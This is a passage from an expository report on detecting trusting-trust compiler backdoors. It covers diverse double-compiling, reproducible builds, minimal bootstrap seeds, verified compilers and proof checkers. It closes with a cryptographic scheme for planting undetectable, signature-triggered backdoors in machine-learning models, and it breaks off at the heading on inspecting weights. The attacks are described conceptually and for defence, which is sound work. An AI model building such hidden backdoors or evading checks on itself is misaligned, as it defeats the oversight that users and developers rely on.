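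This is the most direct test of the method, but an easy one. The compiler was tiny, its code was readable, and Wheeler knew that one of the two binaries was malicious.

#### GCC

The GCC trial tested whether DDC could handle a large compiler in everyday use. Wheeler's colleague Aaron Hatcher first tried to regenerate the GCC binaries that came with Fedora, a version of Linux. He failed, even with help from an engineer at Red Hat, the company behind Fedora, because the Fedora project had not recorded enough about how it built them. Wheeler therefore made his own binary of GCC's C compiler, version 3.0.4, as the suspect. His second compiler came from Intel, a separate company that was unlikely to have copied GCC's code. Intel's compiler could not easily compile three newer versions of GCC that he tried.

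Several details of the build caused problems. GCC stored the full path of the folder where Wheeler compiled it, so both builds had to use the same path. The build instructions also used a standard Linux command with an option that current systems no longer accepted.

The hardest problem to find was in GCC's build process. According to its documentation, GCC compiles itself in stages, and each new compiler rebuilds everything. But the build tool skipped one library's files because their dates indicated that they were up to date. The finished compiler therefore contained some code from the compiler that had started the process, which was Intel's on one side of the comparison and Fedora's GCC on the other. The mistake was unintentional, but it could have helped an attacker, because the rebuild was supposed to replace that code.

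When Wheeler forced the build to include the library, all seven files that make up the compiler matched bit for bit. The largest, the main C compiler, is 6,247,750 bytes.

In both C trials, an honest compiler failed the first comparison, so an initial mismatch is weak evidence of an attack. Finding the cause can take a lot of work in a compiler as large as GCC. A match is much stronger evidence against an attack, because two separately produced six-million-byte files would not be identical by accident. Wheeler did not measure how often DDC would catch a backdoor designed to evade it.

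### Malicious source code

A successful test shows that A does what s specifies, including anything malicious. *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* gives a real example of unwelcome behavior that the method would typically miss. In 2016, users discovered that a version of Microsoft's Visual Studio was adding calls to a data-collection function to the programs it compiled. If the compiler's source specifies those calls, an honest build of the compiler will add them too.

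Someone still has to read the source, and underhanded code can mislead the reader. But Wheeler thinks a trusting-trust attack would be harder to disguise in source than the tricks in the underhanded code contests, because it needs a lot of unusual code and can't pass for a mistake like `=` in place of `==`.

When a compiler is built with a separate parent compiler, the reviewer has to check the parent's source too. Wheeler describes a "pop-up" attack that works when the reviewer fails to do this. The attacker adds a self-copying backdoor to the source of version 2 of a compiler and removes it from the source of version 3. The supplier builds version 3 with version 2, so the new binary contains the backdoor although its source is clean. A reviewer who reads only the source of versions 1 and 3 will not find the backdoor.

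If the user runs DDC with the source of version 2 as p, T will faithfully translate the backdoor, B₁ will insert it into B₂, and B₂ will match the tampered binary. This doesn't contradict the theorem, which assumes that p specifies a compiler that translates s accurately. The source of version 2 does not. A reviewer could find the backdoor by reading that source. The supplier could also remove the need for the older source by having version 3 compile itself and releasing the result. The user would then run DDC with clean source at both steps, and the comparison would expose the backdoor.

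### When separately written programs fail together

DDC assumes that two compilers don't share the same fault, and software engineers have learned to be careful with such assumptions. In N-version programming, several teams separately write versions of the same program, all the versions run at once, and the system uses the majority answer. If each of two versions fails on one input in 1,000 and the failures are independent, both will fail on only one input in a million.

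Knight and Leveson (1986), in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multiversion Programming*, tested whether separately written programs fail independently. Programmers at two universities wrote 27 versions of a program from one specification, and the researchers ran each version on a million inputs. If one of the situations these inputs represent arose every ten minutes, the test would correspond to about twenty years of use.

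More than one version failed on 1,255 of the inputs, roughly ten times as many as independent failures would have produced. On a few inputs, as many as eight versions failed together. *Analysis of faults in an N-version software experiment* (Brilliant, Knight and Leveson, 1990) reports that the versions were extremely reliable individually, but that some programmers had made equivalent mistakes in the harder parts of the problem. The experiment examined only one aspect of the approach, the statistical independence of failures, as Knight and Leveson stressed in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*, so it doesn't show that voting is useless.

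Wheeler replies that DDC requires much less than N-version programming does. The 27 versions had to be right on every input, while T has to be right only on the source of one particular compiler. DDC is also meant to detect a kind of fault that people don't make by accident. Two teams may easily misread the same difficult paragraph of a specification, but they won't both accidentally write code that recognizes `login`, adds a password and copies itself into the next compiler.

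He concedes that two honest compilers could mistranslate the same source in the same way, producing matching binaries that are both wrong. He expects this to be rare because established compilers pass large test suites and usually have to compile themselves correctly. The TinyCC trial gives this view some support, since TinyCC mistranslated itself and GCC did not make the same mistake.

This is a good answer for accidental errors. For deliberate ones, independence can fail for other reasons, because the same attacker could have reached both compilers. Suppose a user runs DDC with three second compilers and gives each a 1% chance of carrying the matching backdoor. If those chances are independent, the probability that all three carry it is one in a million. But if the suppliers built all three with the same older compiler, and that is the most likely way for the backdoor to have got in, the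 probability is close to 1%, and the second and third tests add almost nothing. Compilers with different names and owners can still share an ancestor, which is why Wheeler's advice about the history of T is so important.

Writing a second compiler from scratch avoids some of this shared history, and it may be getting cheaper. According to Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026), people have begun to experiment with N-version programming again because language models have made extra versions of a program much cheaper. A compiler that can build only one program would be enough for DDC. But if the same model helped write both A and T, the user would again have to ask whether the two compilers were independent.

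### Build tools other than the compiler

Malka and colleagues argue that DDC would not catch their tampered `strip`, the tool that adds its payload to finished binaries. The user changes the compiler, but the build still ends by running `strip`. If both builds use the tampered copy, it adds the same payload to B₂ as to A. The two files match, so the user concludes that A is clean.

They are right about a user who changes nothing except the compiler, but the theorem doesn't cover that user. It assumes that the whole system used for the rebuild is free of anything that would affect the result, and a tampered `strip` breaks this assumption. Wheeler's dissertation already names assemblers, linkers and loaders as easy places to hide a trigger, and proposes treating every tool that needs checking as part of the compiler.

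For `strip`, the wider procedure would go like this:

1. On a separate system that contains nothing from the suspect one, compile the source of both the compiler and `strip` with T. Leave the results untrimmed, since a program runs just as well that way, or trim them with an unrelated tool.
2. Use the new compiler and the new `strip` to build both programs again from source, with the supplier's settings.
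3. Compare both results with the suspect copies.

The new `strip` is compiled from clean source by an uncompromised compiler, so it trims the second build without adding anything. The suspect copies contain the payload, so the comparison fails.

The disagreement is therefore more about how much of a system the check would have to include than about whether the method can work. Each additional tool must have source code available and give the same output every time, and the user needs a trustworthy substitute for it during the first build. On NixOS, a user would also have to replace other tools that could carry the backdoor, such as `patchelf`, `cp` and `install`. The operating system that runs the tools could also interfere. Wheeler suggests that "compiler" could be defined to include all the software on a machine, even the programs that start it up.

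Wheeler has not shown that this works in practice. In the GCC trial, he treated the assembler, the linker, the standard C library and the operating system as outside the compiler, so a tampered assembler used in both builds could have gone undetected. The dissertation lists rebuilding an entire operating system in this way as future work. The criticism by Malka and colleagues holds for DDC as Wheeler demonstrated it. The wider version should catch their attack but would take far more effort.

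Even the wider version checks only software. A user can guard against a malicious processor by running the rebuild on a different type of processor, but checking a chip by the same method would require a way to tell whether two chips are equal, even though no two chips are identical the way copies of a file can be. Wheeler considers this the main technical obstacle. The user would also need to know what should be on the chip, and suppliers of ready-made design blocks often forbid even the chip's own designers to see that information. Wheeler mentions an X-ray technique that may be able to map a whole chip without destroying it, but the user would still need the design to compare with the map.

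## Reproducible builds and minimal bootstrap seeds

DDC checks one compiler at a time, but a Linux distribution contains tens of thousands of other programs, which most users download as prebuilt binaries. *Reproducible Builds* (Lamb and Zacchiroli, 2021) describes a way to check those too. If building the same source always gives identical bytes, several independent builders can compile it and compare their results with the published binary.

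The software company Cygnus made its GNU tools reproducible in the 1990s, mainly as good engineering practice. Security became the motive later. Bitcoin Core's developers made their builds reproducible in 2011 so that nobody could slip in code to steal coins. The Tor Browser followed in 2013, the same year that volunteers at Debian, a large Linux distribution, took up the idea.

### Why the same source gives different bytes

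A build's output usually depends on more than the source code. For example, a C program that contains the standard macro `__DATE__` compiles to different bytes on different days. *Reproducible Builds and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux* (Drexel, Hänggi and Méndez Veiga, 2025) sorts 422 known reproducibility issues from Debian's records and finds that three causes account for almost two-thirds of them.

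| Cause | Share of issues | Example | Usual remedy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Times | 30% | The date in a compressed file's header | Give every tool the same fixed date |
| Randomness | 17% | Files in random order inside an archive | Sort the files first |
| Paths | 16% | The name of the build folder inside a binary | Store relative paths, or always use the same folder |

Many tools now take dates from a setting called `SOURCE_DATE_EPOCH` instead of the clock. Projects can also control the build environment. Bitcoin and Tor used minimal virtual machines, which made builds slow and could not remove randomness inside the build. Nix, the package manager behind NixOS, runs each build in a sandbox that contains only the tools listed in its recipe.

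A single program that ignores these conventions can make a package unreproducible. Drexel and colleagues traced one failure to a build script in fwupd, which updates device firmware on Linux. The script compressed a file with Python's own library and stored the current time in the header. They think others missed the problem because most projects use the standard `gzip` tool. The fwupd developers accepted a fix, which helps every distribution that packages the program.

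*Causes and Canonicalization of Unreproducible Builds in Java*, a 2025 study, examines a different remedy, converting both files to a standard form before comparing them. This tolerates harmless differences, but the checker has to be sure that whatever the conversion discards is harmless. Drexel and colleagues defend the strict rule, arguing that a single bit can be the difference between a secure program and an insecure one.

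### What a match proves

Suppose a distribution publishes a binary, and three outsiders rebuild it from the same source with the same tools and get identical bytes. The match rules out tampering that affected only the distribution's build server or download site. To hide such tampering, an attacker would have to compromise all three outsiders' builds in the same way.

Comparing binaries built on separate servers can catch an attack like the one on SolarWinds' Orion software, because a clean server building from the stored source would have produced a different binary. But Orion's source was private, so SolarWinds would have had to make the build reproducible and then run the second build itself.

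Matching builds do not show that the source or the tools are free of malicious code. As Malka and colleagues note about their altered `strip`, rebuilders who share a tampered tool will all produce the same tampered files.

Rebuilders also need to agree on what the source is. Google and Oracle both rebuild popular packages from Maven Central, the main library of Java software. *On the Variability of Source Code in Maven Package Rebuilds* (2026) compares the source code used in those rebuilds with the source released alongside the originals, and examines mismatches in 28 packages with 85 releases. The main cause was build extensions that generate code during the build. When the source code differs, a rebuilt binary may differ from the original without any tampering.

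Even a harmless mismatch can reveal a mistake. Drexel and colleagues found 16 packages in Arch Linux, another distribution, that nobody could reproduce. All belonged to Certbot, which obtains the certificates that websites use for encryption. The packaging script changed its version number after the build system had used the old number to install another component. The official packages were therefore built with a different version of that component than their recipes required.

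### Measured rates

| Software | Period | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Debian 12 | November 2023 | 95.2% of packages reproducible |
| Arch Linux | November 2023 | 75.8% of packages reproducible |
| Nix package collection | Snapshots from 2017 to 2023 | 69% to 91%, with an upward trend |
| Go compiler and tools | Up to February 2026 | Over 2,672 builds, all matching |

The tests behind these figures differ. The Debian and Arch figures come from the Reproducible Builds project, whose test system builds each package twice under varied conditions and compares the results. This tests whether a package can be reproduced, not whether the copy users download matches its source.

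Malka, Zacchiroli and Zimmermann (2025), in *Does Functional Package Management Enable Reproducible Builds at Scale?*, rebuilt 709,816 packages from 17 snapshots of the Nix collection and compared the results with binaries that Nix had published. The snapshots were about four months apart, and the rebuilds ran between June and October 2024. More than 99% of the packages still built, some of them seven years after the original. About 15% of the packages that built but didn't match the published binaries contained a build date.

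Each rebuild downloaded its compiler, other tools and source code from Nix's official store of ready-made files. This let the researchers test packages in parallel and avoid failures where the original source had disappeared from the web. But a tampered compiler in that store would have affected both the old build and the new one, so the study measures how consistently Nix builds packages but can't show that the tools hadn't been tampered with.

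Harmless failures also make tampering harder to detect. In a distribution of 10,000 packages, Arch's rate would leave 2,420 that don't match and Debian's would leave 480. Tampering would stand out in a package that normally matches, but not in one that has never matched, because a mismatch there is expected.

### Who rebuilds and compares

The comparison protects users only if somebody performs it. Drexel and colleagues write that only a few testing platforms exist, most of them run by the Reproducible Builds project. The team added one at the Lucerne University of Applied Sciences and Arts, which checks for new Arch packages every five minutes. It runs on a refurbished PC with 16 gigabytes of memory, although some packages need at least 32, and the team used two larger virtual machines for the initial backlog. A university or small company could afford a similar setup.

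Practices vary among other projects. Bitcoin Core and the Tor Browser test their releases before publishing them. The Go project rebuilds its tools every night. *Reproducible builds in language package managers* (2026) credits the matching Go builds in the table to one outsider, Andrew Ayer. In 2025, Nix regularly monitored only the packages in two of its installation images. *Lila* (2026) proposes a decentralized system for monitoring the rest. As of November 2023, none of the large Linux distributions required its packages to be reproducible. Nobody seems to have counted the users who check a rebuilder's results before installing software.

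The maintainer of Rust in openSUSE, another distribution, argues in *Reproducible Builds* (2024) that reproducible builds take a lot of time and energy and have no effect on supply chain security. "No effect" is an overstatement, because a second build can expose a compromised build server. But making packages reproducible takes the same work even if no independent party ever rebuilds them.

### Would rebuilding have exposed the xz backdoor?

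*Causes and Canonicalization of Unreproducible Builds in Java* lists the xz backdoor among attacks that reproducible builds can prevent. But *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024) points out that reproducibility does not help when the build starts from a compromised source tarball. This is true of ordinary rebuilding, because rebuilders who followed a distribution's recipe would have started from the same tarball. They would have produced matching copies of the backdoored library, and the match would have wrongly suggested that the library was safe.

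Malka (2025), in *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*, argues that the techniques could have caught it. A distribution could instead have compared two builds of the library, one from the release tarball and one from the public repository. The repository lacked the instructions for adding the hidden code, so the second library would be clean. If the build is otherwise reproducible, the two libraries should be identical, so a difference would need an explanation.

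Comparing the tarball with the repository directly is harder, because release tarballs often contain generated files that are not in the repository. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* suggests that developers make the creation of tarballs reproducible as well. Anyone could then regenerate the tarball and spot an unexplained change.

Comparing the two libraries would also have revealed the hidden code only in certain build environments. Freund's report shows that the malicious script added the code only when it detected a Debian or RPM package build. A plain NixOS build is neither, so both libraries would have lacked the code. Jia Tan could also have put the instructions in the repository, where both builds would have included them. The comparison would then have missed them, but anyone reading the repository could have seen them.

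### From 357 bytes to a C compiler

A distribution can guard against tampered tools by building its own from a bootstrap seed small enough for a person to check. Guix, a package manager and Linux distribution, once started from about 250 megabytes of binaries, which its manual describes as next to impossible to audit. In 2023, Guix's *The Full-Source Bootstrap* announced that a dependency graph of more than 22,000 packages now started from a single 357-byte program.

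The seed program, hex0, reads pairs of hexadecimal digits, ignores comments and writes the corresponding bytes. Its own source code is in the same format. For example, one line contains the digits `58` and a comment identifying the byte as an instruction to fetch the number of arguments. A reader can check each byte against the processor's manual. The program can also build a copy of itself from this source, and the reader can convert the digits with an unrelated tool to confirm that the bytes are the same.

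Each tool then builds a slightly more capable one:

| Tool | What it can translate | Tool that builds it |
|---|---|---|
| hex0 | Pairs of hexadecimal digits | The seed |
| hex1 | The same, with one-letter labels for places in the program | hex0 |
| hex2 | The same, with longer labels | hex1 |
| M0 | Named instructions in place of digits | hex2 |
| cc_x86 | A small subset of C | M0 |
| M2-Planet | A subset of C large enough for Mes | cc_x86 |
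| Mes, with its compiler MesCC | Enough C for a modified TinyCC | M2-Planet |
| TinyCC | Most of C | MesCC |
| GCC 2.95.3 | C | TinyCC |

Labels save the programmer from counting bytes. Without them, the programmer has to write the distance of each jump as a number, and inserting a single byte between the jump and its target changes that number. Mes is a Scheme interpreter written in about 5,000 lines of simple C, and MesCC is a C compiler written in Scheme.

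The chain needs a version as old as GCC 2.95.3, released in 2001, because GCC has required a C++ compiler since version 4.8 and the standard C library has required Python since 2018. From there, Guix builds GCC 4.9.4 and then newer versions. GCC 2.95.3 doesn't support RISC-V, a newer processor family, and the first GCC release that does needs a C++ compiler, so developers added RISC-V support to an older GCC that a C compiler can build.

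### The change to Nix in 2026

On January 28, 2026, Nix developers merged a bootstrap that starts from hex0, replacing the older seed used in the strip experiment. One developer confirmed in the developers' chat, *Nixpkgs Stdenv* (2026), that the old archives were gone on the affected platforms. *A Full-Source Bootstrap for NixOS*, a thread on the project's forum, also records the merge and describes support for other processor types as very experimental.

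The new seed is reportedly 181 bytes, which would fit on twelve lines of sixteen bytes each. Neither project page gives the size, but *bootstrapping journey*, documentation from the separate StageX project, gives the same figure for its x86 version of hex0.

On x86 machines, this prevents the attack used in the strip experiment. The build no longer starts with a ready-made `strip`. It builds the first copy from source, so no older copy can add a payload to it. An attacker would have to tamper with the source or something else the build relies on. Platforms that still use the older seed remain exposed to the original attack.

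### OCaml, Go and Rust

A bootstrap chain that ends in a C compiler does not automatically cover other languages. The OCaml compiler, for example, is written in OCaml and comes with a prebuilt binary to compile it. Malka and colleagues describe Camlboot as a stack of simple implementations that builds the OCaml tools from source. Its developers wrote small new programs instead of reviving a long series of old compilers. They then used DDC to compare the result with the existing OCaml 4.07 binary and found no trusting-trust attack in that version.

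Go can still be built starting with only a C compiler, because its own compiler was written in C up to version 1.4. Later releases need an earlier Go compiler. Under the current rule, Go 1.N needs at least Go 1.M, where M is N − 2 rounded down to an even number, so Go 1.26 needs at least Go 1.24. A user can therefore build 1.4, 1.17, 1.20, 1.22, 1.24 and 1.26 in turn.

Rust needs a longer chain because each release normally requires the one before it. A separate compiler, mrustc, can build Rust 1.74 without an existing Rust binary. In January 2026, a participant in the Nix chat estimated that getting from 1.74 to the latest Rust would take about 20 more builds. Nix still used prebuilt binaries to bootstrap Rust and Go, so not every program it packaged was built from its small seed alone.

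### The software and hardware underneath

The seed's size describes only the first program in the chain. Guix's 2023 bootstrap also used a 25-megabyte program, more than 70,000 times the size of the seed, to run the early builds. An attacker who tampered with that program could make it alter the tools while building them. An attacker could do the same through the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, because it handles every file that the tools read or write.

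According to one Nix developer, the new bootstrap still relies on x86 hardware and its firmware, a running Linux kernel, a program that carries out Nix's recipes, and the seed. The live-bootstrap project can build the kernel and Nix from source too. Jansen (2025) used it in a bachelor's thesis to build a full NixOS installation from a small seed. Because live-bootstrap produces a 32-bit system, the process has to build a 32-bit Nix, start a 64-bit kernel and then replace Nix with a 64-bit version.

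Drexel and colleagues call bootstrappable builds a "definitive protective measure" against trusting-trust attacks during the build. This claim is too strong as long as the build depends on a ready-made kernel or build program. They also recommend regular source audits, which remain a large task. A person can read the 181-byte seed in an afternoon, but GCC alone has millions of lines of source code, and even a perfect bootstrap would preserve underhanded code in the source of any of the tools.

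Rebuilding doesn't remove the processor from the list of things a user must trust. As with DDC, a user can repeat the process on a different processor, or in an emulator, and compare the files. The files would differ if a malicious chip altered the tools in only one of these runs, but the comparison would not detect a chip that did not affect the build and acted only on a later trigger.

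## What theory says checks can rule out

Rebuilding a program can show that its binary matches its source, but someone still has to decide whether the source does anything it shouldn't. Mathematicians have proved that no tool can correctly report, for every program, whether it hides a backdoor. The proof doesn't rule out more limited checks, though.

### Rice's theorem and Cohen's virus

Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation, is about what programs do rather than how their code is written. If some programs show a certain behavior and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it shows that behavior.

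The proof builds on Alan Turing's result that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether it eventually stops. Suppose someone had a perfect detector for programs that delete the user's files. For any program Q, they could write a new program that first simulates Q, discarding whatever Q does, and then deletes the files. The new program deletes the files only if Q stops, so the detector would reveal whether Q stops, which Turing showed no algorithm can do for every Q. With small adjustments, the same construction works for any other behavior.

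Cohen (1984), in *Cure of Computer Viruses*, gave a more direct argument for viruses, programs that copy themselves into other programs. Suppose a detector D can recognize every virus. An attacker writes a program that runs D on itself. If D classifies the program as a virus, it does nothing. If D classifies it as safe, it infects other files. D is wrong either way, so for any detector, an attacker can write a program that it misclassifies.

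Neither argument rules out checking one particular program. Cohen described a virus that puts 1234567 in the first line of each file it infects, and a short program that catches it by refusing to run such files. An attacker who knows about this check can change the marker to 123456. A defender can write a detector for any given virus, but an attacker can respond to any detector with a virus that escapes it, so whoever moves second has the advantage.

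Cohen used this idea against Thompson's compiler, without knowing whether anyone had built it. He suggested writing a new `login` and a new compiler so different from the originals that the backdoor could not recognize them in the time a compilation takes.

A checker can also get around Rice's theorem by accepting only the programs it can prove harmless. It then never accepts a harmful program, but it rejects some harmless ones. A checker that rejects everything meets this standard, so a checker's practical value depends on how many harmless programs it accepts.

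The producer can help by supplying a proof. Finding a proof can take an unlimited search, but checking one means going through its steps in order. This also deals with Cohen's contradictory program, because its author would have to supply a proof that it never infects anything, and a valid proof exists only if the claim is true.

### Programs that come with a proof

*Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) applied this idea to operating systems. The kernel publishes a safety policy, and anyone who wants to run a program inside it supplies the binary and a formal proof that the binary obeys the policy. The kernel checks the proof before running the binary. Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* notes that the kernel needs no cryptography or outside authority to do this. It doesn't matter who wrote the program or which compiler produced it, because the proof is about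 the binary itself.

Researchers have recently built systems like this for Linux. Users can load small programs, called eBPF programs, into the Linux kernel after a built-in verifier has checked that they are safe. The verifier tracks the possible range of each value separately, so it rejects some safe programs. Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte (2026), in *Keel*, give the example of a program with an 800-byte buffer. It writes n bytes at the start of the buffer and then up to 800 − n bytes directly after them. The second write ends at byte

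n + (800 − n) = 800

at the latest, so it always fits. But the verifier knows only that n and 800 − n each lie between 0 and 800. It concludes that the second write might reach byte 1,600 and rejects the program.

With proof-carrying code, the kernel specifies the condition to rule out, which here is that the program reaches the second write and writes past byte 800. An untrusted solver outside the kernel then supplies a proof that this can't happen. In this example the proof has 33 steps and takes up 852 bytes. Its central step cancels n against −n, which the verifier could not do by itself.

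The kernel's safety now depends on the program that checks the proofs. Cai and colleagues examined an existing system's checker, which is about 5,000 lines of C, and found 13 bugs. Some of its algebraic rules were wrong, and it accepted some kinds of step without checking them, including one step in the 33-step proof. The researchers showed that an attacker could use forged proofs to get unsafe programs into the kernel.

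Cai and colleagues wrote a replacement checker, Keel, and proved in the proof language Lean that it accepts a proof only if the worrying condition is impossible. Keel rejects the forged proofs. Of 1,891 real proofs, it accepts all that the old checker accepted, plus 16 valid ones that the old checker had rejected. It is also 1.3 times as fast. But they still have to trust the verifier that generates the condition, their mathematical description of C, and the C compiler that builds Keel. A tampered compiler could produce a Keel binary that accepts forgeries.

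Even a perfect checker can show only that a program follows the published policy. If that policy only forbids writing outside a buffer, a program could pass the check and still write a user's password into the buffer.

### Proving that a compiler is correct

A proof can also connect a binary to its source. Leroy's *Formal verification of a realistic compiler* compares two ways to do this. Let S be a source program, C the compiled code, and S ≈ C the statement that C behaves as S allows.

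In translation validation, a separate program checks each compilation after it has happened. A trustworthy validator satisfies

Validate(S, C) = true ⟹ S ≈ C.

Even if the compiler is full of bugs, the validator will reject any wrong translation. No validator can recognize every correct translation, so it also has to reject the correct ones it can't confirm.

A verified compiler comes with a single proof that covers every program it will ever compile:

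Comp(S) = C ⟹ S ≈ C, for all S and C.

An unverified compiler paired with a validator that has been proved correct gives the same guarantee as a verified compiler. This can save work when the validator is much simpler than the compiler.

Leroy and colleagues used both methods in CompCert, which compiles most of the C language. They wrote it mainly in Coq, a proof assistant, which helps people write proofs and checks every step. This approach needs a mathematical definition of C and of the processor's instructions, unlike DDC, which compares one compiler binary with a rebuilt copy.

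The proof measurably reduced accidental errors. CompCert's *Context and motivations* describes a group that spent two and a half years testing C compilers with randomly generated programs. The group reported more than 325 bugs, and every compiler it tested silently produced wrong code. By early 2011, about six processor-years of testing had found no wrong code from CompCert's development version.

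#### Errors in the proof checker

In *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler*, Monniaux and Boulmé (2022) list what could still go wrong. CompCert has had bugs, some of which could make it produce incorrect code without a warning. Coq has had about one critical bug a year, including one that let users prove a false statement by defining a data type with more than 255 cases. In ordinary logic, everything follows from a contradiction, so anyone who can prove one false statement can also prove that a backdoored compiler is correct.

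The two researchers think CompCert's developers are very unlikely to have relied on such a bug by accident, because the mistake would have to look innocent in the source and cause a wrong optimization so rare that testing missed it. This argument is convincing for developers who want their compiler to work, but a malicious producer could search for a bug in the proof assistant and exploit it.

A producer can also introduce a contradiction without any bug. Coq lets developers state axioms, which it accepts without proof. Monniaux and Boulmé give the example of a developer who wants an axiom that a certain whole number is below 10. If the developer types 0 instead by mistake, the axiom is contradictory, because the number can't be negative, and any theorem follows from it. Anyone who accepts proofs from strangers therefore has to read the axioms as well as the theorem, although both are usually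 far shorter than the proof.

#### Proofs written by AI

Proofs about compilers used to take experts months, so it was unrealistic to demand them from a producer. In *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)*, Paraskevopoulou (2026) reports that an AI coding assistant proved one stage of the CertiCoq compiler correct in about 96 hours, writing about 7,800 lines of proof. Human experts had needed several months for a closely related stage. The AI used their proof as a template and had human guidance, but no person wrote any of the new proof.

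*Zero-Trust Formal Methods* describes a project in which people reviewed only the specifications, not the generated code or proofs. This can be reasonable even if nobody trusts the AI, but a false result could still get through, mainly because of bugs in the checker or the wording of the theorem.

### A proved compiler with a tampered binary

Goerigk (2000), in *Compiler Verification Revisited*, showed that a compiler's binary can be malicious even when a proof about its source is correct. The example is the pair of Lisp compilers that Wheeler later used to test DDC. Würthinger (2006), in *Formal Compiler Verification with ACL2*, rebuilt the example step by step.

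The correct compiler produces instructions for a simple imaginary machine, and more than 100 theorems lead up to the main result. If the source program is well formed and the compiled program produces an answer, it is the same answer the source program would give.

A user who builds this formally verified source with the tampered compiler gets another copy of the tampered compiler, as with Thompson's backdoor. Every later rebuild produces the same file, so the tampered compiler also passes the bootstrap test, which requires a compiler to reproduce itself exactly.

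The proof correctly shows that the source text describes a correct compiler, but the tampered binary is not a translation of that text. CompCert could have the same problem. Coq turns most of CompCert into an OCaml program, which an OCaml compiler then turns into a binary. A tampered OCaml compiler could therefore produce a malicious CompCert from a correctly proved source. The DDC comparison of OCaml 4.07 described earlier is useful evidence because it tests the step that the proof leaves out.

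The other remedy is to check the binary itself. Würthinger notes that ACL2, the proof tool used for the source, can also prove properties of the compiled code. In *Will Informatics be able to Justify the Construction of Large Computer Based Systems?*, Goerigk and Langmaack describe a method of closing the gap by rigorously inspecting the compiled code.

### Matching source and binary with prime numbers

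de Oliveira Silva and Quintão Pereira (2025), in *Certified Compilation based on Gödel Numbers*, wanted a check of the binary that needs only arithmetic. They turned source and compiled code into numbers in such a way that the numbers are equal only if the two correspond.

The method comes from the logician Kurt Gödel. Each position in a formula gets a prime number, starting with 2, 3 and 5, and each symbol gets a code, which becomes the exponent. Suppose the code for a is 4, for + is 3 and for b is 7. The formula a + b then becomes

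2⁴ × 3³ × 5⁷ = 16 × 27 × 78,125 = 33,750,000.

Every whole number above 1 has only one factorization into primes, so anyone can recover the formula from the number. The formula b + a gives 2⁷ × 3³ × 5⁴ = 2,160,000, so changing the order of the symbols also changes the number.

The researchers built a compiler called Charon around this idea. One routine reads the source and gives each construct an exponent, such as 79 for an addition, 61 for the start of a loop and 67 for its end. A second routine reads the compiled instructions, looks for the pattern each construct should produce, and gives it the same exponent. If a tampered compiler adds an instruction, the number from the second routine should no longer match the number from the first. The full numbers would be enormous, so Charon stores them as lists of factors.

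The paper sketches proofs that an honest compilation always gives matching numbers and that two different compiled programs never have the same number. A match therefore occurs only when the compiled program is exactly what an honest copy of Charon would have produced. A user with such a copy could learn the same thing by recompiling the source and comparing the files. The prime numbers help mainly if the routines that calculate them are easier to trust than a compiler.

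de Oliveira Silva and Quintão Pereira argue that their method needs no trusted verifier, but this goes too far. The routines are themselves software, written in Python, and a tampered copy could report a match for anything. A suspicious user could work out the numbers by hand, but only for a tiny program.

Charon accepts a restricted version of C, without pointer arithmetic or functions that call themselves. It can't optimize the compiled code, because reordering instructions or reusing the processor's registers would break the match. The researchers tried it on 20 programs. The largest had 145 elements, and calculating the number from its source took about 1.6 milliseconds. They leave for later work any tests against attackers who try to forge a match.

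### Leaks that a single run can't reveal

All these proofs compare what a program does with what it should do, one run at a time. Secrecy is different, because a run can look perfect and still give something away. This Python function checks a four-digit PIN:

```
def check(guess, pin):
    ok = (guess == pin)
    if pin % 2 == 1: time.sleep(0.001)
    return ok
```

The function always returns the right answer, but it takes a millisecond longer when the PIN is odd. An attacker who enters any guess and measures the time learns one bit of the PIN, which cuts the candidates from 10,000 to 5,000.

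A tester who enters the guess 1234 when the PIN is 5679 sees a correct "no" after about a millisecond. That run alone doesn't show a leak, since a function that leaks nothing might take just as long on a slow machine. The leak appears only when the tester repeats the guess with the PIN changed to 5678 and gets the same answer sooner.

Computer scientists call the missing requirement noninterference. Let p be the public input, s and s′ two possible secrets, and Obs everything an outsider can observe about a run. The program P keeps its secret if

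Obs(P(p, s)) = Obs(P(p, s′)) for all p, s and s′.

A requirement such as "never write outside the buffer" applies to each run separately, so one bad run is enough to show a violation. Noninterference is a hyperproperty, meaning a requirement on how runs relate to each other. The test suggested earlier for Meacham's redaction program also checks a hyperproperty, by blacking out two pictures that differ only inside the rectangle.

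No useful PIN check can satisfy the strict formula, because it has to reveal whether the guess was right, and that depends on the secret. The specification must allow this and require only that runs with the same guess and the same answer look alike in every other way. Someone also has to decide what belongs in Obs. The function above passes this relaxed requirement if Obs contains only the returned value, but fails if Obs includes the running time.

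CompCert's theorem covers only observable behavior, which CompCert defines as input, output and how the program ends, excluding execution time and memory use. The theorem would therefore still hold if a compiler turned constant-time source code into a binary that leaks a key through its timing.

A checker can turn noninterference into an ordinary requirement by joining two copies of the program, giving them the same public input and different secrets, and proving that no observer could tell them apart. Testing pairs of runs is easier, but random pairs would almost never reveal a delay that happened only for one particular 64-bit input.

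### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

Rice's theorem rules out a tool that works on every program, but a tool might still catch every backdoor that attackers build in practice. Goldwasser, Kim, Vaikuntanathan and Zamir used cryptography to prove a stronger negative result in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (2022). They showed how to build particular backdoors that no efficient test can find, assuming that certain mathematical problems are as hard as cryptographers believe. Nobody has proved this assumption, but much of today's encryption relies on similar ones.

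#### Testing by queries

Their first construction assumes the checker can only give the model inputs and look at its outputs. It uses a digital signature scheme, in which only the holder of a secret key can sign messages, but anyone can verify the signatures.

The attacker starts with a model that has no backdoor, for example one that classifies pictures, and alters it to check whether some fine details of each picture form a valid signature on the rest. If they do, the altered model gives the answer the attacker wants. Otherwise it gives the original model's answer. The attacker can add a valid signature to any picture by changing those details slightly.

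A checker who found a picture on which the two models disagree would have found a valid signature without the key. If the signature scheme is secure, no efficient method of doing this exists. Someone who looked inside the model might notice the part that verifies signatures, but they still could not make a working trigger, whereas anyone who finds a fixed 64-bit trigger in a program can use it.

#### Inspecting the weights

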